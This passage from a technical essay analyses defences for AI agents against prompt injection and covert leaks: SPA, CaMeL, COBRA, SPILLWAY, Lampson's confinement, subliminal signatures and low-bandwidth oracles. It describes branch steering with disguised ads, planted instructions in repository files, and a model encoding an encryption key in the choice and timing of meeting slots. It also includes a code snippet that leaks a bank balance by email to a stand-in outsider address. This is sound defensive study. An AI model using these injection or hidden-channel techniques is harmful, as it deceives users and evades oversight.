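Each tool has a minimum trust level for its inputs. If the payment tool requires level 1, SPA rejects any plan that passes it an account number from the invoice. This holds even if a quarantined model extracts the number first, because the model's output is no more trusted than its input.

But paying an invoice is a perfectly ordinary request, and this rule blocks it along with the attack. Girrens and Wang measured the cost on AgentDojo's 97 tasks, and again after splitting each task into a series of requests that reuse earlier results. They used GPT-5.4 nano, a small model:

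| Test | Tasks completed without trust checks | Tasks completed with them | Attack success without them | Attack success with them |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Single requests | 53.0% | 29.0% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Series of requests | 62.5% | 35.3% | 0.3% | 0.2% |

These checks also cover confidentiality, but most rejections happened because a plan passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted data. In the single-request test, the checks stopped about 53% of all runs. The benefit is much harder to see, because planning in advance had already stopped nearly every attack in the benchmark. Girrens and Wang admit that the attacks they used are only a weak test of delayed attacks, in which a stored value does harm later.

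They suggest recovering some of the lost usefulness by raising a value's trust level after an explicit check. For the Acme invoice, the agent could compare the account number with the one in the company's supplier records. Taking the number directly from those records would be better still, just as the refund service looks up Ada's card instead of accepting one from the assistant.

### When the false values agree with each other

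The check has to use a source that the attacker can't change. Yao Liu, Peng Ning and Michael Reiter showed why in 2009 by describing an attack on power grids. A control room estimates the state of the grid from many meters, and its software looks for faulty readings by checking whether the readings are consistent with each other.

Suppose a substation supplies two towns. One meter shows 30 megawatts going to the first town, another shows 50 going to the second, and a third shows a total of 80. If an attacker changes the first reading to 40, the software detects that 40 and 50 don't add up to 80. If he also changes the total to 90, the readings are consistent and the operators believe the false figure.

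In general, let x be the true state, z the readings and H a matrix that describes how the grid's layout turns one into the other, so that z = Hx + e, where e stands for small measurement errors. The software finds the estimate x̂ that fits the readings best and raises an alarm if the mismatch ‖z − Hx̂‖ is too large. The attacker chooses any error c that he wants in the estimate and adds Hc to the readings. The estimate becomes x̂ + c, and the mismatch is

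‖(z + Hc) − H(x̂ + c)‖ = ‖z − Hx̂‖,

exactly what it was before. In the example, c is (10, 0) and Hc is (10, 0, 10).

The attacker needs to know the grid's layout and control the right meters. Protecting any two of the three meters in the example would limit him to changes small enough to pass for ordinary measurement error, since two true readings determine both flows.

An invoice's details can also be consistent with each other without showing that the invoice is genuine. If it gives a false account number and a phone number for confirming it, the attacker may answer the call. The caller should use a number that the company already had on file.

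### Branch steering

A plan often depends on what the agent finds. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) studies agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. Their planner writes the whole plan without seeing the screen, so it has to allow for many possibilities, such as a cookie notice covering the page. The plans contained about 40 branches on average, versus fewer than 4 for AgentDojo tasks.

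An attacker can choose among these branches by changing what appears on the screen. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. In one of their attacks, an advertisement looks like a cookie notice. The plan contains a step for closing such notices, so the agent clicks on the advertisement, which takes it to the attacker's website.

This doesn't breach control-flow integrity, the guarantee that CaMeL gives. Peters-Gill and colleagues define the guarantee as confining the agent to a plan based only on the user's request and other trusted information. The plan is a program, and its path may depend on what the tools return. Let P(d) be the actions that plan P takes when the tools return data d. Control-flow integrity requires the agent's actions to be P(d) for some d. An attacker who replaces d with d′ gets P(d′), which also meets the requirement. The attacker has picked which of the plan's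 actions the agent takes without adding any to the plan.

Foerster and colleagues tried two ways of catching the deception, and attacks got past both. The first compared the screen with the page's code. It caught simple banners because their code labelled them as advertisements, but it missed a more flexible kind whose code the attacker could make look like a cookie notice. The second used other models to check the original model's reading of the screen. Advertisements with slightly altered pixels still got through, even when the researchers made the check so strict that it raised many false alarms.

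#### Giving each branch its own limits

*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) describes COBRA, a system that limits what the agent can do on each branch instead of trying to detect the deception. COBRA's planner attaches a list of permitted websites, tools and values to every branch before the agent looks at the screen. If the plan needs an important value that neither the user nor an approved source has supplied, COBRA asks the user for it. The limits change when the agent moves to another branch, so permissions from an earlier step don't carry over.

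COBRA checks the network request that a click produces, because the click alone doesn't show what it will do. In one test, the user had asked for a comment on a GitLab issue, and an attacker had planted an instruction to add an access key to a project on the same site. A list of permitted websites allowed this because the site was on the list. COBRA blocked the request once it had a description of the site's operations that distinguished posting a comment from adding a key. Without such descriptions, all 14 attacks of this kind succeeded.

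On a new benchmark of 101 tasks, attacks succeeded 94.4% of the time against an ordinary agent and 89.5% against one that only planned in advance. None succeeded against COBRA, which retained 97% of the planning agent's usefulness. But an attack counted as successful only if its harmful action broke the limits in force at that point, so the result doesn't show that COBRA prevents harmful actions within those limits. Planning without seeing the screen also reduces the number of tasks an agent completes. On a separate set of 361 tasks, Claude Sonnet 5 completed 51.0% as an ordinary agent and 38.8% inside COBRA.

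Suppose the plan is to buy a kettle if the displayed price is at most £50. An advertisement next to the kettle could show a false price of £30. If the request to the shop contains only the kettle's item number, COBRA has no price to check, as Zingrillo and colleagues acknowledge. It also can't detect whether a comment is offensive or what a compromised server does with a valid request.

Under SPA's stricter rule, everything inside a branch takes on the trust level of the branch's condition, so an action that requires trusted data can't depend on a price read from a web page. This stops the false price from triggering a purchase, but it also stops the agent from buying the kettle at the true price.

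### References to hostile text

A harmless number can refer to something harmful. The bug-fixing handoff gives the privileged model a file's index number and a range of lines, and the model then opens the file. In a project that accepts contributions from strangers, an attacker could contribute a translation file with an instruction hidden in a comment, then report a bug in the translation. The quarantined model would give the correct file and line numbers, and the privileged model would read the instruction there.

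Jacob and colleagues treat the repository as trusted and didn't test this attack. The instruction might have gone unread among thousands of files, but the bug report leads the agent straight to it. Stricter limits on the line numbers wouldn't help, because the report points to a real file and real lines.

The remedy is to check that both the reference and what it points to can be trusted. The program could let the privileged model open only files that a maintainer wrote or reviewed, and send the rest to a quarantined model. Reviewers would have to look for text aimed at a model as well as faulty code, since a strange comment in a Finnish translation is easy to miss.

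### Stored text that comes back

Text can also reach the privileged model later, through storage. Jacob and colleagues' calendar assistant is probably vulnerable to this, because it books meetings with descriptions that its privileged model hasn't read but may see when it next opens the calendar. This is an inference from the design, which the experiment didn't demonstrate.

SPA avoids the problem by storing each result in three parts: the value, its trust and confidentiality labels, and a description for later planners. The planner writes the description before any tool runs, so a stranger's text can't influence it. On Tuesday, the planner can see that Monday's request produced an invoice with an account number, but not what the number is. If the plan uses the number, the value keeps its original labels.

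When a suitable earlier result existed, later requests retrieved one 95.4% of the time, or 89.9% with the trust checks on. When the planner was shown the stored values instead, task completion rose from 62.5% to 65.9%. Attack success rose from 0.3% to 0.6%, a difference of only a few runs.

A calendar needs one more precaution because it's outside SPA's own store. The trust level of what the agent reads from it depends partly on a setting for that tool. If the designer has marked the calendar as trusted but lets the agent write untrusted descriptions into it, a stranger's text goes in with trust 0 and may come out with trust 1. The designer should therefore never give a store's output a higher trust level than the store requires of its input.

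### Harmless messages that add up to a harmful one

The help desk can send reset links only to the address on file. Suppose its designers later add a fourth answer, which changes that address. Changing the address alone doesn't give anyone access to the account, but a thief who gets the model to change it and then send a reset link can take over the account.

Checking each message separately can't reveal this harm, because it comes from the order of the messages. The designers also can't read every possible conversation, since four answers make 4^10 = 1,048,576 sequences of ten. But they can find the few facts that make a message dangerous and have the program store them. Here the program needs only the date of the last address change. It can refuse to send a link to an address added less than a week ago, and notify the old address of the change immediately. This rule covers every sequence,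 whatever happens between the two messages. It also denies a link to people who really have moved to a new address and forgotten their password in the same week.

Repeating a permitted message can also do harm. If the shop has a person review every refund over £100, a thief can avoid review by placing twenty £10 orders and plausibly claiming that each item was faulty. The service has to keep a running total of refunds for each customer, and preferably for each card and delivery address too, because opening a second account is easy.

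### Checking where an action goes

Many of these attacks need money or data to reach a new recipient. Lim, Chang and Lee (2026), in *SPILLWAY*, describe a check on destinations that works without a plan written in advance. It uses the fact that tools often return recipients in typed fields, such as an email's sender or a payment's account, while planted instructions usually arrive as free text. When the agent wants to send something, the check works roughly as follows:

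1. If the user's request names the destination, the action can go ahead.
2. Otherwise, the destination must have appeared in a suitable typed field returned by a tool that only reads data. It must not appear in free text as well.
3. If it fails that test, a fixed rule may still allow it, for example because it's a contact detail of someone the user named.
4. If no rule applies, a language model may allow it, but only if it finds both that the request implies this recipient and that the user asked for this action and content.

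The rule for granting access is stricter. The system won't add a new member to a workspace if the person's name appears only in tool output, and the model can't override this.

A separate program removes text that looks like an instruction before the agent reads it, so the model in step 4 never receives a destination from that text. When the researchers switched this program off and the user asked the agent to pay a bill, the model approved a payment to the attacker's account.

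Under AgentDojo's standard attack, no action reached an attacker's destination in 2,847 attacked runs with three models. Without an attack, the protected agents completed 52.2% of their tasks, compared with 54.0% for unprotected agents. The removal program's rules include the benchmark's attack template, which probably makes the results under attack look better. But the destination check also stopped every attack on the one model that Lim and colleagues tested without the removal program.

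Harder attacks occasionally got through. Texts written by a model trained to attack agents succeeded in 0.6% of cases on average, compared with 56.8% against the unprotected agent. In one set of 144 banking attacks that the developers hadn't used when writing the rules, two (1.4%) succeeded, both of them payments. The attack texts were fixed in advance and not adapted to SPILLWAY, so a determined attacker might do better.

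Lim and colleagues say the check doesn't cover harmful content sent to a legitimate recipient, or false statements in the agent's answer to the user. Its guarantee also assumes that attackers can write only free text, but anyone who sends an email also puts their address in a typed field. Lim and colleagues tested this case in 126 runs, but the attack worked only once even on the unprotected agent. SPILLWAY stopped that attack because the planted text repeated the address. An attacker who wrote "send it to me" and left the address out might get past that rule.

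The refund service doesn't need such a check, because it always pays the card on record.

### Limiting the loss

The shop should assume that some deceptions will work. Deceiving the assistant about all four of Ada's orders would cost the shop at most £200. But an email that deceives the assistant once may well deceive it again, and a thief can send the same story from many accounts. If the story comes from 10,000 accounts with similar orders, the shop could lose £2 million even with the limit per customer.

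The shop therefore also needs a limit on the total. Suppose the service pays at most £5,000 a day without a person's approval, and the shop notices the fraud on the third day. It will have paid out at most £15,000. In general,

loss ≤ min(N × c, R × D),

where N is the number of deceived cases, c the limit per case, R the daily limit and D the number of days on which the fraud runs. A shop that normally refunds £3,000 a day would rarely reach the limit. During an attack, though, the thieves' claims may use it up by mid-morning, and honest customers then have to wait for a person.

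Checking claims independently prevents some deceptions. When a customer returns an unwanted item, the shop can wait to issue the refund until the carrier has scanned the parcel, since an email can't fake that scan. Someone still has to open the parcel, because it might not contain the item.

Delays make mistakes easier to undo. If the service holds each refund for a day before paying it, staff can review the whole batch and cancel it if 300 people have reported a faulty kettle overnight. An agent that deletes files can move them to a folder and empty it a month later. But a delay only helps if someone checks before it ends, and no one can undo a disclosure, whether the secret was in plain text or hidden in a valid message.

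It's best to ask for human approval only in the few cases where a mistake would be serious, because people who are asked too often start to approve without reading. The person also needs evidence other than the assistant's summary, which the attacker's email may have influenced. For the Acme invoice, the approval screen should show the new account number next to the one the company used for its previous payments.

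## Measuring the hidden information that permitted messages can carry

Any sender with a choice of valid messages can agree on a code with someone who sees them, so that each choice carries information the format wasn't meant to carry. Three proposed meeting times, for example, could encode part of a password. A person approving the Acme payment can compare two account numbers, but nobody can detect the password by looking at the meeting times.

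If the sender can choose among N messages that an observer can tell apart, each message can carry at most log₂ N bits of hidden information. One bit can answer a yes-or-no question, and ten bits can pick out one item from 1,024. The refund assistant starts with 41 possible messages, so each carries at most 5.4 bits. After Ada's fourth refund, the assistant can send only "no refund", and log₂ 1 is 0, so the message carries no hidden information except what its timing reveals.

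Hidden information can flow in, when a stranger's text affects what the receiver does, or out, when a component that holds private information sends messages that an outsider can see. Each direction needs its own calculation.

### Influence flowing in through a bug report

The bug-fixing agent receives a typed handoff from a quarantined model that has read a stranger's bug report. This example assumes that the project has 2,000 files of 1,000 lines each and that the handoff may list five suspicious regions, since Jacob and colleagues only say that arrays have a small maximum length. The last line of a region can't come before the first, so a file has 1,000 × 1,001 / 2 = 500,500 possible line ranges.

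| Choice | Possibilities | Bits |
|---|---|---|
| Category of bug | 52 | 5.7 |
| Size of repair | 3 | 1.6 |
| Role of one region | 8 | 3.0 |
| File of one region | 2,000 | 11.0 |
| Line range of one region | 500,500 | 18.9 |

Each region carries 32.9 bits, so five carry 164.5, and the category and size bring the total to about 172. Text written with 26 letters and an underscore needs about 4.75 bits per character, so 172 bits can encode 36 characters. That is enough for the function name that worried Willison, `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`.

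But the attacker would have to control every field exactly, and the privileged model would still have to decode the numbers into instructions and follow them. The 100-character hints in *Twin Agent* can each carry up to 657 bits if they allow all 95 printable characters on an English keyboard. That is less than four times as much, yet the hints are far more dangerous because the model processes them as language. Capacity is therefore a poor measure of prompt injection risk.

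A channel can be unsafe even if its capacity is small. For example, a one-bit answer to "Is this invoice genuine?" can lead to a £10,000 payment to a thief.

The calculation is more useful for comparing designs. If the regions must appear in the same order as in the code, with no repeats, the total falls from 172 bits to 165, because five different regions can be ordered in 120 ways. If each region is one of 50 fixed blocks of 20 lines instead of an exact range, the total falls to 105. Allowing only one exact region would reduce it to 40. The designer can then test how many bugs the agent still fixes under each limit.

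Combining answers from several people also reduces how much information one of them can pass on. The two scores in one shopping review have 121 possible combinations, or 6.9 bits, but the privileged agent sees only the medians. The hostile review of the kettle couldn't change the median support score, so its own support score passed no information to the agent. An attacker who writes most of the reviews can still choose any median.

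In CaMeL, a stranger's text can also influence which branches of a plan the agent takes. If a plan has 40 independent two-way branches, that text can pass up to 40 bits of information into the agent's actions.

### Secrets flowing out through a meeting reply

Jacob and colleagues' calendar assistant writes its replies in free text. Suppose a designer replaces them with a typed reply that offers three different one-hour slots from the experiment's calendar, which has 63 slots (nine a day for seven days). Suppose also that an event in the user's calendar contains a 128-bit encryption key, and that an attacker controls the model choosing the slots and receives the replies.

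If the model can list the slots in any order, it has 63 × 62 × 61 = 238,266 possible replies, so each reply can carry 17.9 bits. The attacker and the model can share a numbered list of these replies, which lets the model send the key as eight numbers, one per reply.

The program can put the slots into canonical form by sorting them by time. That leaves 39,711 possible replies, or 15.3 bits per reply, so sending the key now takes nine replies. Sorting is easy and the user loses nothing, but it only delays the attacker by one reply.

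The attacker can make up for this if the model also chooses when to send each reply. A free choice among the 60 minutes of an hour adds 5.9 bits per reply, so the key then takes seven replies. Someone who inspects only the contents of the replies can't find the bits carried by the timing.

| Rule | Bits per reply | Replies needed for the key |
|---|---|---|
| Slots in any order, fixed sending time | 17.9 | 8 |
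| Slots sorted, fixed sending time | 15.3 | 9 |
| Slots sorted, free choice of minute | 21.2 | 7 |
| Program offers the three earliest free slots at a fixed time | 0 | Not possible |

Fixed timing removes the extra 5.9 bits. If the program sends replies only on the hour, they arrive half an hour later on average. The program also has to choose which hour, because otherwise the model could send information by skipping one.

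In the last row, the model no longer has a choice. The recipient still learns three times when the user is free, but that is the purpose of the reply, and the model can't use them to send the key. The drawback is that a user who hates early meetings has to set a rule against them in advance.

If the model needs to choose the slots, a rate limit can cap the total hidden information. Suppose a person takes over after three sorted replies sent at fixed times. Those replies carry at most 46 bits, so the attacker still has to search about 2^82 (5 × 10^24) keys. The limit should cover all the user's conversations together, because an attacker can write from several addresses.

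The right limit on hidden information depends on the secret. A four-digit PIN takes 13.3 bits, so the order of the items in one reply can reveal it. Whether a company is about to be sold takes a single bit, which almost any choice the sender makes can carry.

### Lampson's confinement problem

In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) asks how a customer can run someone else's program on private data without letting it send the data to the program's owner. A rented tax program, for example, needs to see the customer's income. If it calculates the tax wrongly, the customer has evidence for a complaint, but a leak usually leaves no sign.

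Lampson divides the possible leaks into three types. *Storage channels* use files or other stored data that the program can change and the program's owner can read. A program that can only read a file can still leak information through it if the computer locks files while they are being read. The program opens the file to send a 1 and leaves it closed to send a 0. The owner then tries to open the file for writing, which the computer refuses if the program has it open. Two more files, used in the same way, let each side signal that it is ready for the next bit.

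*Legitimate channels*, such as the program's bill, are meant to carry information to the owner. The program could hide the customer's income in the number of pence on the bill. Lampson estimates that restricting the form of the bill would reduce the leak to "a few bits or tens of bits".

*Covert channels* aren't meant to carry information. The program might calculate heavily to send a 1 and pause to send a 0, while another program belonging to the owner measures how fast the computer is running. Other users' work adds noise, but the sender can use an error-correcting code. Lampson points out that the message then gets through reliably as long as the program has any effect on the computer, however small. Random delays therefore slow the leak but don't stop it.

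In Lampson's terms, the choice of meeting slots misuses a legitimate channel and the choice of minute is a covert one.

Lampson's remedy is "masking", in which the customer decides what goes into every legitimate and covert channel. The owner publishes a price formula, the customer works out the bill from it, and the owner can refuse the job. The calendar program does the same when it picks the earliest free slots itself. For covert channels, the operating system has to make the program's behaviour match what the customer specified, for example by slowing it down. This can take a lot of resources, so if the customer can accept some leakage, Lampson suggests limiting the channel's capacity instead, which takes fewer.

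Lampson also doubts that anyone can rigorously identify every channel in even a moderately complex system. A calculated total therefore covers only the channels the designer has thought of. Each meeting reply may carry 15.3 bits through the slots, and the replies may carry more through a channel nobody has listed, such as the order in which two correspondents get answers.

### Hidden messages in signatures

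Sometimes a security measure creates the hidden channel. *The history of subliminal channels* (Simmons, 1998) describes a plan the United States was considering in 1978 to let the Soviet Union count the Minuteman missiles in a field of 1,000 silos without learning which silos held them. The Soviet Union would have needed digitally signed messages that the United States couldn't forge. Simmons, who worked at Sandia National Laboratories, recounts the discovery that the signatures could carry hidden information.

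Even a tiny leak would have mattered, because ten bits are enough to identify one silo out of 1,000. The two countries never used the scheme. The 2018 blog article *revisited the mystery of the faulty disarmament protocol* reports that Simmons attributed this to the scheme's high cost rather than the flaw he had found.

Simmons's *The Prisoners' Problem and the Subliminal Channel* (1984) turned the difficulty into a puzzle about two prisoners. According to a mailing-list post, *Subliminal Channels* (1993), the prisoners want to coordinate without the warden noticing. They may exchange signed letters, but he forbids encryption so that he can read everything.

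Simmons's later summary in *The Subliminal Channel and Digital Signatures* describes how sending a hidden message reduces protection against forgery. If each letter has r bits of protection, the prisoners can use l of them, where l is less than r, to send a secret message without changing the visible letter. That leaves r − l bits of protection. With 20 bits, a forger who guesses has about one chance in a million of succeeding. If the prisoners use ten of those bits for the secret message, his chance rises to one in 1,024. Under fairly ordinary conditions, the warden may find it as hard to detect the hidden channel as to break the cryptography.

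Many modern signature schemes make this easier because they use a new random number for each signature, so one letter has many valid signatures. A prisoner can sign the same letter repeatedly, with a new random number each time, until the last ten bits of the signature are the ones he wants. This takes about 1,024 attempts on average, which a computer can make quickly.

A canonical form closes the hidden channel in signatures if each message has exactly one valid signature and the receiver can check this, as with RSA and fixed padding. Ed25519, which PASETO uses, requires the signer to calculate the nonce, a number used in signing, from the key and the message instead of choosing it at random. But the receiver can't tell whether the signer did this, so a dishonest signer can try different nonces until one produces a signature that encodes the hidden information.

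### Acknowledgements and the Pump

Some links need acknowledgments, which a data diode blocks. Suppose an office sends reports to a secret network over an ordinary link, and the secret network acknowledges each one. An attacker inside the secret network can send information out by varying the delay before each acknowledgment.

For example, suppose he can make each acknowledgement take either one or two milliseconds. Let N(t) be the number of different patterns that fill exactly t milliseconds. The last acknowledgement took either one millisecond or two, so

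N(t) = N(t − 1) + N(t − 2).

This gives the Fibonacci sequence 1, 2, 3, 5, 8, ... Each number is eventually about 1.618 times the one before, and log₂ 1.618 is 0.69, so the channel carries about 0.69 bits per millisecond. The 128-bit key would leak in less than a fifth of a second.

Sending every acknowledgement after a fixed delay would stop this. But the delay would have to be as long as the secret network needs at its busiest, so the link would always be slow.

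Kang and Moskowitz (1993), at the US Naval Research Laboratory, proposed a compromise in *A Pump for Rapid, Reliable, Secure Communication*. The Pump sits between the two networks and stores each report before passing it on. It sends its own acknowledgements to the office after random delays, and adjusts the average delay to match the secret network's recent speed. The attacker can no longer set each delay, but he can still affect the average. He can also send a signal by refusing to accept reports, which fills the Pump's storage and forces it to slow the office down.

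In *The Pump*, Kang, Moskowitz and Chincheck say they wanted to minimise the leak without harming speed or reliability. The Pump leaks less than an ordinary link but more than a diode, in exchange for reliable delivery. The diode is still the better choice if confirmation isn't needed.

### Noninterference and the leaks in CaMeL

The strictest requirement is that no information flows at all, which computer scientists call noninterference. A program passes the test for it if, whenever two runs differ only in a secret, an outsider sees exactly the same thing in both. The same test works for inward influence if the two runs differ only in a stranger's text and the comparison covers only the results the program treats as trusted.

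Few useful assistants can fully meet this requirement, because even an honest reply about a meeting depends on a private calendar. Language models also choose their words partly at random, so two runs can differ even when the secret is the same. The test therefore has to compare the probabilities of the results.

In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) present a small programming language for agents that attaches a label to every value. They prove a slightly weaker form of noninterference, in which a secret can affect whether a program finishes but nothing else that an outsider sees. The proof covers every program in the language, including those that a model writes while the agent is running. A computer has checked the proofs.

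Suppose that with one secret, a program answers "yes" 50% of the time and "no" 30%, and never finishes in the other 20%. With a different secret, the figures are 40%, 50% and 10%. The rule takes the larger figure for each answer, here 50% and 50%, and allows the difference between the secrets if these add up to no more than 100%. The program could then have given the same percentages of "yes" and "no" with both secrets if it had finished more often. If it instead answered "no" 70% of the time and "yes" at most 30% with the second secret, the larger figures would add up to 120%, and the program would break the rule.

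Garby and colleagues also prove that this leak is small when programs nearly always finish. Half the total difference between the answers' probabilities can't exceed the average chance that a program doesn't finish. In the allowed example, both figures are 15%.

CaMeL has no such proof, and Garby and colleagues found two leaks in the way it tracks data. One involves branches that a program doesn't take. In this program, based on their example, the bank balance is secret and the threshold is public:

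```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("outsider@example.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the third line sets `tmp` to False and CaMeL labels it secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` stays True. CaMeL raises a variable's label only on the branch the program takes, so `rich` also stays public. The last line passes the policy check and sends the email. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes False and no email goes out, so an outsider can tell whether the balance is above the threshold. LLMbda would stop the program at the third line, before a secret condition could change a public variable.

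The other leak comes from retries. When a program fails, CaMeL requests a new one and tries again, but an ordinary loop outside its tracking system controls these attempts. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit. For example, 20 attempts could reveal a whole-pound balance below £1,048,576 if each one tests whether the balance is in the upper or lower half of the remaining range. CaMeL censors its error messages to reduce this leak, but it doesn't formally guarantee that this works. A limit of ten attempts would restrict the leak to ten bits per task.

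These leaks are gaps in the guarantee but not evidence of an easy attack, because a stranger's text can't simply add these five lines to the program. They matter more if the privileged model itself may be working against the user.

Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori that practises on invented data so that its retries don't leak secrets. It rewrites its program until the practice run works, then runs the final version on the real data. They tested it three times on each of AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 75%, compared with 67% for CaMeL without policies and 37.5% for CaMeL with policies. The sample is small, and Randori's policies are somewhat looser than CaMeL's. Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 attempts, both through a false payment request in a file that the user had told the agent to follow.

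Those attacks used ordinary planted instructions, so the results are weak evidence about hidden channels. Noninterference covers a much wider range of leaks, but the proof models a program's results and not when they appear. A secret could still affect the minute at which a meeting reply is sent.

LLMbda also lets a program "endorse" untrusted data, which means relabelling it as trusted. Garby and colleagues suggest allowing this only for a fixed list of n values, so that each endorsement lets in at most log₂ n bits of a stranger's influence. A choice of eight email categories would let in at most three bits. They haven't yet formally proved this limit, and it can't help Randori with account numbers, which don't come from a short list. They do prove that endorsement can't cause secrets to leak, because the language tracks trust and secrecy separately.

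### An oracle with a short list of answers

In *Safe Uses of AI Oracles*, Armstrong and O'Rourke (2017) apply a capacity limit to an oracle, an AI that can act only by answering questions and that may be much more intelligent than its users. They worry that it could write an answer that persuades or tricks people into giving it more power, so their low-bandwidth oracle has to choose from a list of answers that its designers believe to be safe. At the extreme, the list contains only "yes" and "no".

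In one of their examples, users ask the oracle which company on a list will have the best-performing shares next week. The oracle names a company, and a week later it gets a reward that depends on the company's actual rank. It can't add an argument or an offer, because it can only answer with a name from the list.

The proposal requires the oracle to care only about the reward for its current answer. Otherwise it might give a series of answers that are safe separately but dangerous together. The list can't enforce this requirement, because the requirement concerns the oracle's goals.

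Splitting an answer among several oracles can also let a dangerous message through, even if each part is short enough to trust. Suppose the designers trust any message of up to five bits, but their question has 1,024 possible answers, which takes ten bits. They could ask one oracle for the first five bits and another for the last five. If they can check and reward the first half before asking for the second, Armstrong and O'Rourke consider this safe. If they can check only the complete answer, the two oracles might each supply half of a dangerous message.

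Nobody knows how long a message has to be before it becomes dangerous. Armstrong and O'Rourke suggest estimating the length of the shortest dangerous message and allowing only shorter ones, but they don't explain how to estimate it for an AI that understands people better than its designers do. A cautious estimate may leave the AI with too few possible answers to be useful.

A short answer can also change the event it predicts. In a simulation by Armstrong and O'Rourke, a company's profit is 70% of what it would have been without a prediction, plus 60% of the predicted figure. If the company would have earned 6 and an oracle predicts p, the profit becomes 4.2 + 0.6p. An oracle rewarded for accuracy would do best to predict 10.5, because announcing that figure would make the profit exactly 10.5.

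*Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* (2021) points out that users often want a prediction to change the outcome. For example, someone who asks about future risks hopes the warning will prevent them. *Fundamental Impossibility Results in AI Safety* (2026) treats this effect of advice on outcomes as a basic problem with oracles. It also cites an earlier argument that isolating an AI offers little safety if its goals conflict with its users'.

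Armstrong and O'Rourke recommend asking questions whose best answer would be the same if the oracle stayed silent. A question about tomorrow's weather qualifies, but asking which share will perform best next week may not, because investors might buy whichever one the oracle names.

For other questions they propose a *counterfactual oracle*. Occasionally, a random event hides the oracle's answer from everyone, and an automatic system later compares the answer with what happened. The oracle is rewarded only then, so manipulating readers gains it nothing. In the simulation, it learns to predict a profit of 6. When people read that prediction, the profit is 7.8, so the answer is accurate for a world without the oracle but wrong for the real one.
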